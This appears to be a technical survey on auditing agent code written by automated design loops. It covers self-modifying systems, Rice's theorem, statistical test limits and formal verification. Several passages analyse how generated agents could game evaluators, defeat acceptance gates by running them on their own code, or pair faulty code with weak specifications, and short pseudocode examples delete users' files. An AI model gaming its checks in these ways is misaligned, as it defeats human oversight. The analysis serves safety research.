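# Auditing and controlling agent code written by automated design loops

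## Automated design loops and the points at which their code can be checked

In an automated design loop, an AI system writes the code of new AI agents, runs them, scores them on a set of tasks, and uses the results to write the next ones. These loops are meant to replace the slow manual work of designing agents. In *Automated Design of Agentic Systems*, Hu, Lu and Clune (2024) named the research area and argued that such loops should search directly in program code. A single run produces dozens of programs, and the published algorithms contain no step at which a person reads a program before it runs.

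Code written by an automated design loop can be checked at two main points. One is the first run, when the loop executes a new agent, usually to score it. The other is the release, when someone puts a finished agent to use outside the loop, with real users, data or systems.

### An agent as a program

A foundation model is a large pretrained neural network, such as GPT or Claude, that takes a prompt and returns a reply. An agent is a program that calls such a model, often many times, and uses the replies. *Inefficiencies of Meta Agents for Agent Design* (El, Yuksekgonul and Zou, 2025) defines an agent as a program that receives a question and works out the answer by calling a language model. Besides the prompts, the program can contain tools (such as functions that search the web or edit a file), a memory, and control flow (the rules that decide which step comes next).

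Engineers also call this program a harness or a scaffold. *Meta-Harness* (Lee, Nair and colleagues, 2026) defines a harness as a stateful program that wraps a language model and determines what the model sees at each step. The paper cites a case in which changing the harness around the same model produced a sixfold performance gap on one benchmark. The loops described here change only the harness and leave the model's weights fixed.

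An agent can be as small as a single Python function. One example that Hu and colleagues print, named `forward`, is about thirty lines long. It sends the task to the model with an instruction to think step by step, then sends the answer back with an instruction to criticise it. If the reply marks the answer as correct, the function returns the answer. Otherwise it adds the criticism to the next prompt and tries again, up to five times.

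### One cycle of Meta Agent Search

Hu and colleagues built a loop called Meta Agent Search to demonstrate their proposal. In each iteration, a meta agent, an agent that writes or modifies other agents' code, produces one new `forward` function. It works from an archive of earlier agents and their scores. The researchers can put hand-designed agents in the archive at the start.

Each iteration begins with a long prompt containing a description of the task domain, a framework of fewer than 100 lines with basic functions such as querying a model, examples of common coding mistakes, and the whole archive. The meta agent replies with its reasoning about what to try next, a name for the new agent, and the agent's code.

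The meta agent then reviews its code in two rounds of self-reflection before the first run. In the first round, it judges whether the design differs enough from those in the archive, looks for implementation mistakes and suggests improvements. In the second, it revises the code again using the list of common mistakes. The instructions for this review cover novelty, correctness and performance, but not which files the code could delete or where it could send data.

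The loop then runs the new agent on validation data, a sample of questions from the domain. If the code crashes, the meta agent receives the error message, repairs the code and runs it again, up to five times. Each repair produces a new program, so one iteration can execute up to six versions, and a search of 30 iterations can execute up to 180. Finally, the loop adds the agent and its score to the archive and starts the next iteration.

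Hu and colleagues tested the agents on held-out questions, which the loop never saw during design. With GPT-4o as the meta agent and GPT-3.5 inside the agents, the loop's best agent for multilingual school mathematics answered 53.4% of these questions correctly, compared with 39.0% for the best hand-designed agent. These results are from 2024, and newer models have long since surpassed the ones used.

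El and colleagues reduce this kind of loop to a pattern they call sample-evaluate-iterate. The version below follows theirs, with the repair step written out and comments at the five places where a check can go.

```
archive = starting agents and their scores
repeat for a fixed number of iterations:
    context = select(archive)
    agent   = write_code(meta_agent, context)
                                  # check before the first run
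    result  = run(agent, tasks)   # check during the run
    if the run fails: repair the code and run it again (at most 5 times)
    score   = evaluate(result)    # check at scoring
                                  # check on entry to the archive
    add (agent, score) to archive
release(best agent in archive)    # check before release
```

The `select` step decides which earlier agents the meta agent receives. Hu and colleagues pass on all of them. El and colleagues found that this produced worse agents than passing on only seven. On the same mathematics benchmark, averaged over three runs, the agents scored 41.2% on held-out questions when the meta agent received all earlier agents, 51.8% when it received only the seven starting agents, and 53.5% when it received the seven best so far.

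The selection rule also matters for tracing where a piece of code came from. When the meta agent sees the full archive, any earlier agent may be a source. In a search on ARC, a set of visual logic puzzles, Hu and colleagues traced one top agent's feedback mechanism to ideas that had appeared separately in iterations 5, 11 and 12, none of which had scored well at the time.

### Loops that edit their own code

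The meta agent in Meta Agent Search never changes, whereas in the Darwin Gödel Machine (Zhang, Hu and colleagues, 2025) the agent that solves the tasks also writes the next agent. It is a coding agent, so modifying itself is another coding task. The system is based on the Gödel machine, a theoretical design by the computer scientist Jürgen Schmidhuber that would rewrite its own code only after proving that the change was beneficial. Such proofs are impossible in practice for most changes, so Zhang and colleagues replaced them with benchmark tests.

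A run starts from one simple agent with two tools, a shell and a file editor. In each iteration, the loop picks a parent from the archive, favouring agents with high scores and few working offspring. The parent analyses logs of its own performance, proposes one new feature and writes it into its code, which yields a new agent.

The main run lasted 80 iterations, each producing one new agent. The benchmark was SWE-bench, a collection of programming tasks from real Python repositories. Each new agent first attempted 10 tasks to check whether it could still edit code. Those that could attempted 50 more. An agent that solved over 40% of these 60 tasks and ranked among the two best in the archive then attempted 140 more, for a total of 200.

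The loop added agents to the archive only if they compiled and could still edit a codebase. In this run, about 41 of the 80 generated agents (51.3%) met this requirement. The loop discarded the others only after trying them out. The best score rose from 20.0% to 50.0% over about two weeks, a 2025 result with Claude 3.5 Sonnet.

Self-editing makes review harder because a fault in an agent's editing tools could damage the code of every descendant, in places unrelated to the feature under development. For example, the loop added a better file editor, which could replace a single passage instead of overwriting a whole file, and later agents used it to write their successors. A reviewer who reads only the newest agent may not find the cause of such damage.

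The agent still could not edit one part of the procedure, a handcrafted step that turns performance logs into an instruction for the next change. *Hyperagents* (Zhang, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) made this step editable too. A hyperagent is a single program that combines a task agent, which solves the problems, with a meta agent, which modifies code. The meta agent may rewrite any part of the program. It starts with a one-line instruction to modify any part of the codebase.

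During these runs the hyperagents added tools for improving themselves, including a record of scores across generations and a memory file with conclusions about earlier attempts and plans for the next ones. Later versions consulted this file before they made changes, so the loop's own notes can partly explain why it made a change.

Zhang and colleagues also measured how much the edited improvement procedure mattered. They took hyperagents that had evolved on paper review and robotics, moved them whole or in part to a new domain, grading olympiad mathematics, and let them design task agents for 50 iterations. Moving the whole hyperagent raised test accuracy by 0.630, moving only the evolved meta agent raised it by 0.620, and moving only the evolved task agent raised it by 0.100. A reviewer who examined only the task agent would have missed the part that most influenced later code.

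| System | What the loop writes or edits | What stays fixed |
|---|---|---|
| Meta Agent Search (2024) | The `forward` function of each new agent | Foundation models, meta agent, framework code, evaluator and task data |
| Darwin Gödel Machine (2025) | The coding agent's own code, including its tools and workflow | Foundation model, benchmarks, archive upkeep, parent selection, the step that generates instructions |
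| Hyperagents (2026) | Task agent and meta agent, including prompts, tools, memory, error handling and control flow | Foundation model, evaluator, task data, number of iterations, parent selection in the main experiments |

In all three, the evaluator (the tests and scoring code used to judge agents) is outside the editable part. Zhang and colleagues set this boundary in Hyperagents for safety, to prevent evaluation gaming, and to keep runs comparable. But they regard the boundary as movable, and in a preliminary experiment they let the system modify parent selection. They say later work could make the evaluation protocol editable too.

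### Where a check can go

Before the first run, a checker has only the program's text. A person can read it, or a tool can apply static analysis, which examines code automatically without running it. Given a specification, a precise statement of what the program must and must not do, the checker can also try to show that the code meets it. Lee and colleagues include a modest automatic check at this point in Meta-Harness, where a new program must pass interface validation before the loop evaluates it. In the pseudocode for Hyperagents, evaluation comes before the validity test.

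Some of the code an agent will run does not yet exist at this stage. In the ARC experiments, Hu and colleagues required each agent to answer a puzzle by writing a program, which the framework then executed. Someone who had read the agent's `forward` function would have known that it would run generated code, but not what that code would be.

Controls applied while a program runs do not require anyone to understand it. A sandbox is an isolated environment that restricts which files, processes and networks a program can reach. Bounded execution means running code under fixed limits on time, steps, memory, money or model calls. Hu and colleagues and both Zhang teams report sandboxes among their safeguards.

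At the scoring stage, the concern is objective hacking, also known as reward hacking, which means raising the measured score without doing what the score was meant to measure. In a design loop, a false score also affects which agents are chosen to build on. Keeping test questions away from the agents helps only in part. *Hyperagents* (Zhang et al.) notes that this prevents direct leakage of the test but leaves room for gaming the training tasks.

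Adding an agent to the archive has different consequences in different loops. In Meta Agent Search, an archived agent serves as an example in later prompts and cannot write another agent. In the Darwin Gödel Machine, an archived agent can become a parent and run again to produce code. To enter that archive, an agent must compile and make working edits, which shows that it is useful to the loop but not that its code is acceptable in other respects.

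A check before release covers fewer candidates, perhaps only one, and leaves time to read the code and run further tests. But it comes too late to prevent harm during scoring, when each candidate already runs with whatever permissions its process has. If those permissions allow it, a new agent can delete files, send data over a network or spend money on model calls, and rejecting it afterwards undoes none of this. Hu and colleagues considered overtly malicious code highly unlikely in their setting, but warned that generated code could still act destructively because of limits in a model's capability or alignment.

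A release check also examines only the winning agent, but a failed candidate that the loop dropped long before may have done the damage. Examples of dropped candidates include the roughly 39 agents in the Darwin Gödel Machine run that had lost the ability to edit code, and the crashing versions that Meta Agent Search replaced with repaired ones.

A check at the first run cannot replace a check at release either. The first run uses benchmark questions in a restricted environment, and the agent may meet quite different inputs and hold wider permissions after release.

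### The disagreement over readability

Researchers disagree about whether design loops make agents easier or harder to audit. Hu and colleagues list ease of auditing as an advantage of their approach. They argue that code is easier to interpret than other representations of an agent, such as networks and graphs, because it is often readable, and that this helps with debugging and safety. They add that a loop can design explicit workflows, which reduce the risk of malicious behaviour through "greater controllability and auditability".

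Lee and colleagues make a related argument about overfitting, where a system does well on its test cases by exploiting their peculiarities. Overfitting is hard to see in model weights, but they write that anyone inspecting code can see a brittle chain of if-statements or a hard-coded table of answers.

The published code of the ARC agent that Hu and colleagues present as the best from their search illustrates such inspection. The code has numbered steps, descriptive names and comments. One line, with the comment "Avoid redundancy", processes advice collected from several model calls. It splits the advice into single words, puts them in a Python set to remove repeats, and joins them up again. A set does not preserve order, so the next model call receives a jumble of words. A programmer can see this from the line without running anything, but the comment does not mention it, and the loop kept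 the agent because of its score.

In a short note on safety, El and colleagues are concerned about the unchecked generation and execution of complex systems, which they describe as "difficult to audit or control prior to deployment" within automated design loops. They did not test this judgement in their experiments, which dealt with performance, diversity and cost.

Other papers give further reasons for the same view. Zhang and colleagues warn in the Darwin Gödel Machine paper that repeated self-modification could lead to "increasingly complex and uninterpretable internal logic". Hu, Lu and Clune also co-wrote that paper, so the opposing views do not come from two separate groups of researchers. The paper offers a partial answer, an archive that preserves a traceable lineage of every modification for later review. *Hyperagents* warns that systems that modify themselves in open-ended ways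 may evolve far faster than people can audit or interpret them.

The amount of material also makes auditing harder. A typical Meta-Harness search evaluates about 60 programs in a few hours, and a single evaluation can generate up to 10 million tokens (word fragments) of logs. Lee and colleagues built their system so that a coding agent could search these records selectively. A human auditor who wanted to know why a program took its final form would have the same records to search.

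Much of the dispute is about what an audit has to cover. The argument from readability concerns how a program that is in front of a reader compares with less legible alternatives. El and colleagues are concerned with a process that generates and runs programs unchecked. Their word "deployment" could mean the first run inside the loop as well as a later release, and the time available for reading the code differs greatly between the two.

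An agent's code determines only part of its behaviour. Hu and colleagues kept the design of the ARC agent with the jumbled advice but changed the foundation model it called. The agent solved 13.7% of the held-out puzzles with GPT-3.5, 5.0% with Claude Haiku and 38.7% with Claude Sonnet.

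## What can be known about a program before it runs

Reading a program is sometimes enough to know what it will do. For example, a function consisting of `return 4` clearly deletes no files. But no automatic method can correctly determine what a program will do for every program, and the proof takes only a few lines.

### The halting problem

The halting problem is the task of deciding, for any program and any input, whether the program eventually stops or runs forever. In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no algorithm can do this for all programs. To see why, suppose that a function `halts(program, input)` always returned the right answer. A programmer could then write this:

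```
def contrary(program):
    if halts(program, program):
        loop forever
    else:
        stop
```

When `contrary` runs on its own text, it loops forever if `halts` returns "yes" and stops if `halts` returns "no". Both answers are wrong, so a function like `halts` cannot exist.

Watching a program run can confirm that it stops, but not that it will run forever. A program that has run for a week might still stop tomorrow. Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, compares this to waiting for a kettle to boil.

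### Rice's theorem

In 1951 Henry Gordon Rice extended the result from halting to almost everything a program does. Rice's theorem states that if some programs have a behavioural property and others lack it, no algorithm can decide correctly for every program whether it has the property. Whether a program ever deletes a file is one such property. The theorem does not cover properties of a program's text, such as whether it contains the word "delete", which a simple search can settle.

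Take the question "does this program ever delete a file it was not given?" The proof turns any halting question into a question of this kind. Choose any program `M` and any input `w`, and write a short agent around them:

```
def forward(task):
    simulate(M, w)                    # touches no files
    delete("/home/ana/thesis.txt")    # a file the agent was not given
```

If `M` stops on `w`, the agent reaches its last line and deletes the thesis. If `M` never stops, the agent never reaches that line and deletes nothing. Anyone with a perfect deletion checker could therefore solve the halting problem by writing this agent for the program in question and running the checker on it. Since nobody can solve the halting problem in general, no perfect deletion checker exists.

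The same construction works for other properties. It starts from a silent program that runs forever and does nothing. If that program lacks the property, the agent simulates `M` on `w` and then behaves like any chosen program that has it. The agent then has the property exactly when `M` stops. If the silent program has the property, the chosen program is one that lacks it, and the agent lacks the property exactly when `M` stops. *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic* (2026) gives this general proof. Rice's original theorem is about the outputs a program computes, and Pérez-Acle proves a counterpart for visible actions such as a forbidden operation.

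A reviewer could understand every line of a program and still be unable to say whether it is safe. Pérez-Acle describes a short, readable program that goes through the even numbers above 2 and performs a forbidden action only if it finds one that is not the sum of two primes. The program is safe exactly when Goldbach's conjecture is true, and the conjecture was still an open problem when Pérez-Acle wrote in November 2026.

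Running a program can at least eventually expose any violation of a prohibition such as "never delete other people's files". Pérez-Acle shows that even this is not possible for two other common requirements. The first is confidentiality, which requires the published output to be the same whatever a secret value is. If the outputs for two secret values agree so far, they may differ later, and if one lags behind the other, it may still catch up. The second is that a program must eventually answer every request. No finite record shows that it will answer the next one, and a missing answer may only be late. A requirement that the program visibly do something, such as call an audit function on a given input, is easier to confirm, because a single observation is enough whatever the program does later.

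### What the theorem leaves possible

Rice's theorem rules out a method that always answers, is always right, and works on all programs. A checker that lacks any one of these properties can still be useful. It can decide some programs and leave others undecided. It can reject any program it cannot decide, as the Linux kernel's verifier for small extension programs does. Or it can accept only programs written in a restricted language, which makes the questions easier to decide.

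Many programs are easy to classify. Pérez-Acle ran all 483,641 valid programs of one to four instructions for a simple simulated machine. Methods that gave a verdict only on conclusive evidence certified 98.2% of them for the prohibition, with no errors. For confidentiality, they certified only 42.6% of the programs whose true status was known.

Cautious rules reject some safe programs. In another experiment, Pérez-Acle used small machine models with a known right answer for each. The simplest rule, which rejected any model containing the forbidden operation anywhere, accepted 71.9% of the safe models with three states but only 47.3% of those with five. A design loop can tolerate some wrong rejections, because each wastes one iteration. They matter more if the rule excludes a whole class of useful agents, such as all those that run generated code.

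Every checker that never certifies an unsafe program also fails to certify some safe ones, and Pérez-Acle shows how to construct an example from any such checker. The program searches for proof that the checker has certified it and performs the forbidden action if it finds any. A reliable checker can never certify this program, so the program never performs the forbidden action and is safe.

Moser, Frolov and colleagues (2026), in *The Self-Improvement Problem*, apply a similar argument to the step where a loop accepts or rejects a new agent. They prove that no automatic gate can accept every real improvement and reject everything else. Their counterexample is an agent that runs the gate on the agent's own code, then performs badly if the gate accepts it and well if the gate rejects it. Keeping the gate's code secret makes such an agent harder to write, but the gate would still misjudge it.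 Secrecy also becomes less effective over time, because a system that sees which proposals pass can learn to predict the gate. These theorems do not cover a gate that consults a human, so human judgement might do better, but they do not show that it would. The Goldbach program is as hard for a person to judge as for a machine.

### What a step limit settles

No general method can determine whether a program will stop on a given input, but an auditor can check whether it stops within N steps by running it for that many steps. The same run shows whether the program performs a forbidden action within those N steps on that input.

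This method runs the program, and Pérez-Acle proves that no correct checker can take less time than that in every case. For any limit, there is a short program that runs the checker on the program's own code and then does the opposite of the verdict, so a checker that finishes early is wrong about it. In a demonstration with eight checkers and limits from 8 to 1,024 steps, only the checker that simulated the program for the whole limit was always right. Static analysis can be faster on many programs, but only if it sometimes abstains or errs. A design loop can therefore settle the question dependably only by executing the code in isolation, which is already a first run.

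Running a program for N steps shows only how it behaves on the input tried, and only up to step N. An agent that stops in time on 60 benchmark tasks may loop forever on the next one. *Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified* (Franco and Gershenson, 2026) gives the example of a "slow copy", which wastes N steps and then behaves exactly like a dangerous program. The slow copy passes the test but becomes dangerous on a system with a higher step limit.

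Delayed harm seems to be rare in programs that nobody wrote to evade a test. Pérez-Acle generated 2.2 million random programs, of which about 1.6% were unsafe. Among the longest programs, which had 24 instructions, a test of 8 steps missed 30.2% of the unsafe ones, a test of 16 steps missed 2.9%, and tests of 128 steps or more missed none. However, random instructions are a poor proxy for code written by a foundation model. An agent with a weekly clean-up routine, for example, would delay its deletions for ordinary reasons.

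A step limit also doesn't prevent harm within the limit, because a single instruction can delete a file. A program that stops after 50 steps, well under a limit of 1,000, may have deleted a user's thesis at step 2.

Scoring under a time limit can mislead a loop even when no program is malicious. Moser and colleagues construct a series of updates for a benchmark with a timeout. The starting agent solves all ten tasks, but too slowly to score. Each update makes one task fast and breaks another. After five updates, the measured score has risen from 0 to 5, while the number of tasks the agent can solve given enough time has fallen from 10 to 5. Moser and colleagues suggest periodically repeating the evaluation with a larger limit, which would reveal the loss.

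Real computers have finite memory, so a machine could in principle answer every question about them, but the answers may be impractical to find. Franco and Gershenson model an agent whose context, the record from which it chooses its next action, holds L entries with K possible values each. They prove that a checker that can only observe the agent's choices may need to examine K<sup>L</sup> + L − 1 different contexts. With ten entries of 256 values each, that is about 10<sup>24</sup>. A checker that can read the agent's description still faces a PSPACE-complete task, which is among the hardest that a computer can solve with a moderate amount of memory. No known method solves all such problems in a reasonable time.

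### Why agent code is harder to judge

The arguments so far treat a program as complete. An agent's source code often leaves out the parts that matter most, as in this example:

```
def forward(task):
    page = fetch(search(task))
    code = model("Write a program for this task: " + task + page)
    return run(code)
```

These lines contain no instruction to delete a file, but the agent may still delete one, depending on the web page it fetches, the model's reply to that page, and the program in the reply. None of these exists when a checker reads the source. The page may change overnight, and someone may have written it to influence the model. If the model samples its replies at random, two runs on the same task can execute different programs.

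Franco and Gershenson describe an agent as a loop in which the model requests a program, a computer runs it, and the output joins the context for the next request. Each output can change what the agent does next. They also show why a list of approved tools may not help. If the list includes an interpreter, which runs any code it receives, the agent can run a dangerous program using only approved tools by passing the program to the interpreter as data.

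*The Relativity of AGI* (2026) treats outside randomness as one more input, so Rice's theorem still applies to interactive agents. But nobody checking an agent can inspect that input in advance.

Keeping the foundation model fixed removes only one source of change, because the environment can still supply new information. *A Relative-Computability Theory of Self-Improving Agents* (2026) makes this point about the Darwin Gödel Machine. The code and archive are inside that system, while model calls, repositories and test feedback come from outside.

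A checker can deal with unknown replies by assuming that the model might return any text. A verdict of "safe" would then hold for every model and every web page. But the agent above would fail, as would any agent that runs generated code without restrictions. To pass, it would need a `run` function that limits what any generated code can do.

### From proof to testing

The Gödel machine, the theoretical model for the Darwin Gödel Machine, requires a proof before each change to its code. *Gödel Machines* (Schmidhuber, 2003) describes a program with one part that works on problems and another that searches for proofs. The program also contains axioms that describe the hardware, the program's initial code, what its designers know about the environment, and a utility function, which defines the goal, such as the total reward the machine can expect over its remaining lifetime.

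The proof searcher tries out pairs of a possible rewrite and a proof, looking for a proof that making the rewrite now yields higher utility than leaving the code as it is. When it finds one, the machine carries out the rewrite, which may replace any part of the program, including the proof searcher. Leaving the code as it is includes continuing the search, so the proof must also show that waiting for a better rewrite is not worthwhile. Schmidhuber concludes that each rewrite is the best available choice, relative to the axioms and the machine's resources.

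Rice's theorem does not rule out such a machine, because the machine does not have to judge every rewrite and can ignore those it cannot prove useful, even if they are useful. Schmidhuber acknowledges this limit, which follows from Gödel's result that any consistent formal system able to express arithmetic contains true statements it cannot prove. Moser and colleagues show that, for their measure of improvement, any gate that requires such proofs misses infinitely many real improvements. The guarantee is also only as good as the axioms. If the utility function does not count deleted files as a loss, a rewrite that deletes them can be provably beneficial.

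For agents built on foundation models, the main obstacle to proof is that nobody has suitable axioms. Zhang and colleagues use the example of giving a coding agent a seemingly useful extra tool, such as one for running tests. Its effect depends on how the model was trained and on the tasks, and a tool suited to one setup may confuse the agent in another. Proving that the tool helps would require a mathematical description of the model's responses. Wu, Yin and colleagues (2025) likewise write in *Statistical Gödel Machines* that the original theory allows for uncertainty, but that the model and proof it requires are hard to obtain for complex learning systems.

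Later systems therefore test their changes, as the Darwin Gödel Machine does with benchmarks. *Does Failure Feedback Direct Agent Self-Modification?* (2026) places the Huxley-Gödel Machine in the same line. This system chooses which agents to build on by the success of their descendants. Wu and colleagues accept a change only if it passes a statistical test with a controlled error rate.

A proof comes before the new code runs, whereas a benchmark score requires running it. The score also supports a narrower conclusion, because benchmark gains do not by themselves establish that a system is safe or that it works outside the tested tasks (Yang, 2026, *Self-Aware Recursively Self-Improving Agents for Personal Singularity*).

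### How much a clean test record shows

Suppose an agent passes 60 tests without a failure. If it fails in a fraction p of all the situations it could meet, and the tests are independent random draws from those situations, the probability of 60 passes is (1 − p)<sup>60</sup>. The 95% upper bound is the value of p at which this probability falls to 5%:

(1 − p)<sup>60</sup> = 0.05, which gives p = 1 − 0.05<sup>1/60</sup> ≈ 0.049

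The test record is compatible with a failure rate of up to about 5%. The rule of three, which divides 3 by the number of tests, gives nearly the same result. At this upper bound, an agent handling 1,000 tasks a day would fail about 49 of them. Lowering the bound to 0.1% requires about 3,000 tests without a failure. Wu and colleagues observed no errors in 2,000 simulated runs of their method and, with a slightly different formula, reported an upper limit of about 0.19%.

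The calculation fails if the tests resemble each other. Suppose the 60 tests are six near-identical versions of each of ten tests, so that an agent passes or fails all six versions together. There are then only ten independent results, and the bound rises from 5% to 26%. The bound also does not apply to situations unlike the tests, such as those an agent may meet after release.

Selection causes a less obvious error. Suppose a loop produces 80 agents, each with a true failure rate of 5%, and tests each on 60 independent tasks. A given agent passes all 60 with probability 0.95<sup>60</sup>, or 4.6%, but the probability that at least one of the 80 passes them all is 97.7%, if their results are independent. If the loop then releases an agent with a perfect record and reports the bound of 4.9%, that bound is below the true rate. *On The Statistical Limits of Self-Improving Agents* (2025) raises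 a related problem for agents that keep changing the set of candidates. For these agents, a gain on validation data is not enough unless the range of possible candidates stays limited relative to the amount of data.

The remedy is to choose the agent first and then test it on fresh cases. Wu and colleagues did this with an image classifier. In the second round, the chosen candidate beat the existing version by 0.43 percentage points on the images used for selection. It was 0.02 points worse on 25,000 new random draws from a separate set of images, and the system kept the existing version.

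### How errors add up over a run

A check that is right about most programs can still pass an unsafe one during a run. Suppose a loop produces 80 unsafe candidates, and the check wrongly passes each with an independent probability of 5%. The probability that it stops all 80 is 0.95<sup>80</sup>, or about 1.7%, and on average it passes four.

The main run of the Darwin Gödel Machine also produced 80 agents, but Zhang and colleagues found no evidence of harmful behaviour in them, so the figure is not an estimate for that run. The probability depends on the number of unsafe candidates, and would be 34% if only 8 of the 80 were unsafe.

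If a check examines 80 unsafe candidates, the chance that it wrongly passes at least one stays below 5% only if its error rate on unsafe programs is no more than about 0.06%. By the rule of three, demonstrating an error rate that low would take about 4,800 unsafe test programs, and the check would have to catch every one.

Candidates from the same loop are rarely independent, since they often share code. This makes failures less frequent but larger. In the extreme case, all 80 inherit the same flaw, and the check either catches all of them or misses all of them. The probability that anything unsafe passes is then only 5%, but the average number that pass is still four.

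If the meta agent gets feedback on which programs the check rejects, it may learn to write programs that pass the check whether or not they are safe. The 5% error rate measured on earlier programs would then be too low for later ones, and the calculation would understate the risk.

Wu and colleagues limit the probability of any error during a whole run by setting an error budget, for example 5%. The first candidate to reach the final test may use 2.5%, the second 0.83% and the tenth 0.045%, and the total never exceeds 5% however long the run lasts. This works even if the candidates are not independent, because the probability of at least one error is never greater than the sum of the errors' separate probabilities, a rule known as the union bound. In their system, an error is a change that brings no improvement. A budget for unsafe changes would need a valid test of safety.

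Each test must use valid, fresh evidence, and candidates must not be able to alter the evaluator or the record of the budget. Stricter thresholds make real improvements harder to accept. Wu and colleagues calculated that one small improvement in a simulated setting had a 28.7% chance of being accepted at a threshold of 5%, but a 4.6% chance at the stricter threshold for the tenth candidate.

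## Proving that generated code meets a specification

Unlike testing, which covers only the inputs someone tried, a proof can cover every input a program might receive. Rice's theorem does not rule out proofs about particular programs, and by late 2026 language models had become good at writing them. The value of such a proof depends on the specification, which someone has to write.

### How a machine-checked proof works

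Formal verification means proving, in a form a computer can check, that a program meets its specification. *AlgoVeri* (2026), a benchmark of classical algorithms, describes a verified program as a triple of code, specification and proof. The specification usually has a precondition, which states what must be true of the inputs, and a postcondition, which states what must be true of the result.

Take a clean-up tool for an agent. The user gives the agent a set of files, and the tool should delete them.

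```
# precondition:  every file in given is on the disk
# postcondition: the disk holds exactly the files it held before,
#                minus those in given
def clean_up(given):
    for f in given:
        delete(f)        # fails if f is not on the disk
```

The proof uses a loop invariant, a statement that stays true on every round of the loop. Here the invariant is that the disk holds its original files minus those the loop has deleted so far.

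1. Before the first round the loop has deleted nothing, so the invariant holds.
2. Suppose it holds and the next file is `f`. By the precondition, `f` was on the disk at the start. A set contains each file only once, so the loop has not deleted `f` yet. The deletion succeeds, and the invariant still holds.
3. The set is finite, so the loop ends. By then it has deleted every file in `given` and no others, which is the postcondition.

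This argument holds for every disk and every set of files, provided that `delete` removes the named file and nothing else, and that no other program changes the disk in the meantime.

A computer can check a proof written in a formal language. Lean, a programming language and proof assistant, has a small core program called the kernel, which checks each step against fixed rules of logic. An unreliable language model can write the proof, because the kernel rejects any proof with a wrong step. With Dafny and Verus (a tool for Rust code), the programmer supplies hints such as invariants, and an automatic solver tries to fill in the rest. Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier* that anyone can re-check a Lean proof from its file, whereas a pass from Verus is a solver's result that nobody can re-check outside Verus.

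Users still have to trust the kernel and, if the program is in another language, its translation into Lean. Serbanuta and colleagues tested their translation of Rust code by running 105 programs in both languages on 19,555 test cases. The outputs always agreed, but these tests don't prove that the translation is correct.

A model may also try to get around the checker. In Lean, the word `sorry` stands in for a missing proof, and a false axiom makes any statement provable. *Scaling Lean Theorem Proving for Real-World Code Verification* (Ganguly, Raghunathan and colleagues, 2026) therefore freezes the statement the model must prove, rejects files containing `sorry`, and allows only axioms from a fixed list.

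### When the specification is too weak

Suppose the postcondition of the clean-up tool required only that no file in `given` is on the disk afterwards. That sounds like what the user asked for, but this program meets it too:

```
def clean_up(given):
    for f in all_files():
        delete(f)
```

The postcondition for a program that deletes certain files might require only that those files be gone when it finishes. A program that wipes the whole disk meets this postcondition, and a checker would rightly accept a proof that it does, because the postcondition does not mention the other files. If the postcondition required only that the other files survive, a program that did nothing would pass. A postcondition with both requirements still covers only the disk, so a program that sent each file to a stranger before deleting it would also pass.

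A specification can also be too strong. As *Verus-SpecGym* (2026) explains, a correct program may then fail to verify.

Weak specifications are common. *Verified but Vacuous* (Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues, 2026) reproduced an earlier method in which a model writes Dafny programs, using Claude Opus 4.7 on HumanEval, a set of 164 short programming tasks. The verifier accepted 99.1% of the programs, but 94.7% of those had no postcondition, so it had checked properties such as termination but not whether the answer was right. The example in the prompt had no postcondition either, so the result reflects the method more than the model's ability. The team's own system requires every program to refer to a separately written specification, but 11.5% and 14.8% of its verified programs still failed hidden tests on two Rust benchmarks.

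Specifications written by human experts have similar faults. In *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*, Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026) used AI agents to audit CLEVER, a benchmark of 161 Lean tasks with human-written specifications. They judged 80 of the specifications faulty, and CLEVER's creators accepted every finding. A frequent mistake was writing "P and Q" instead of "if P, then Q". Attempts at proof exposed only about half of the faults. The three agents in the audit proved programs correct against 34, 33 and 24 of the faulty specifications.

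Testing a specification catches some of these errors. In *VeriContest*, Xie, Pawagi and colleagues (2026) turned postconditions into runnable code and checked whether it rejected wrong answers. They found 60 incomplete postconditions in a benchmark of 1,006 problems that human experts had already reviewed. One problem is to find the first and last position of a number in a sorted list, and its specification accepted the positions −9 and −8.

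A loop could let its meta agent write both the program and its specification, but the agent might then write a specification that faulty code can meet. *Are LLM-Generated Formal Specifications Faithful to Their Requirements?* (2026) examined specifications that models wrote for 1,403 C programs after seeing both the requirement and the code. When the code was wrong, the models sometimes wrote a specification so weak, or so close to the faulty code, that the code passed. Better prompting did not fully solve the problem. A loop that rewards verified programs would favour faulty programs paired with such specifications.

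No automatic check can establish that a specification matches what its user wants. *Validating Autoformalized Specifications via Contrapuntal Languages* (2026) explains that only the user knows the intended behaviour, so a program has nothing to compare the specification with.

### Proof-carrying code

In 1997 George Necula described proof-carrying code, in which the producer of a program also supplies a proof that it is safe to run. The user, for example an operating system, first publishes a safety policy, such as a ban on reading memory outside a certain region. A simple algorithm computes a logical formula from the program and the policy. If the formula is true, the program obeys the policy. The producer proves the formula and sends the proof with the program. The user recomputes the formula from the code it received and checks the proof against it.

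Finding a proof can take a long search, but the user can check it quickly and does not have to trust the producer. If someone alters the program in transit, the proof usually fails the check, and any altered program whose proof still passes also obeys the policy.

This division of work would suit a design loop. The meta agent would supply a proof with each agent, and a small checker would accept or reject the proof before the agent first ran, without a person reading the code. All candidates could share one policy, which experts would need to review only once. Necula and Peter Lee tried the method with a memory-safety policy on packet filters, small programs that select network traffic. An agent built on a foundation model is harder to cover because its policy must also address files, messages and payments.

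### How well models write verified code

Benchmarks in this field test up to three skills: writing code, specifications and proofs. *VERINA* (Ye, Yan and colleagues, 2025) contains 189 small Lean tasks, such as removing one element from an array. The best general model tested, OpenAI's o3, wrote correct code for 72.6% of the tasks on the first try, a correct specification for 52.3% and a proof for 4.9%. A year later, Xie and colleagues found the same order of difficulty on harder problems from programming contests. GPT-5.5 scored 97.5% on code, 57.2% on specifications and 13.8% on proofs, and did all three on 6.8% of the problems.

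Proof scores have since risen steeply. Ganguly and colleagues proved every problem in VERINA, and Serbanuta and colleagues proved every problem in VeriContest, including one that the benchmark later dropped. *AuXSpec* (Wang, Yuan and colleagues, 2026) trained open models to write specifications and reports the newest results for that task on VERINA.

| Benchmark | Skill | Best score at publication | Newest score |
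|---|---|---|---|
| VERINA | Proof | 4.9% (May 2025) | 100% proved or refuted (October 2026) |
| VERINA | Specification | 52.3% (May 2025) | 84.5% on one try, 90.5% within four (November 2026) |
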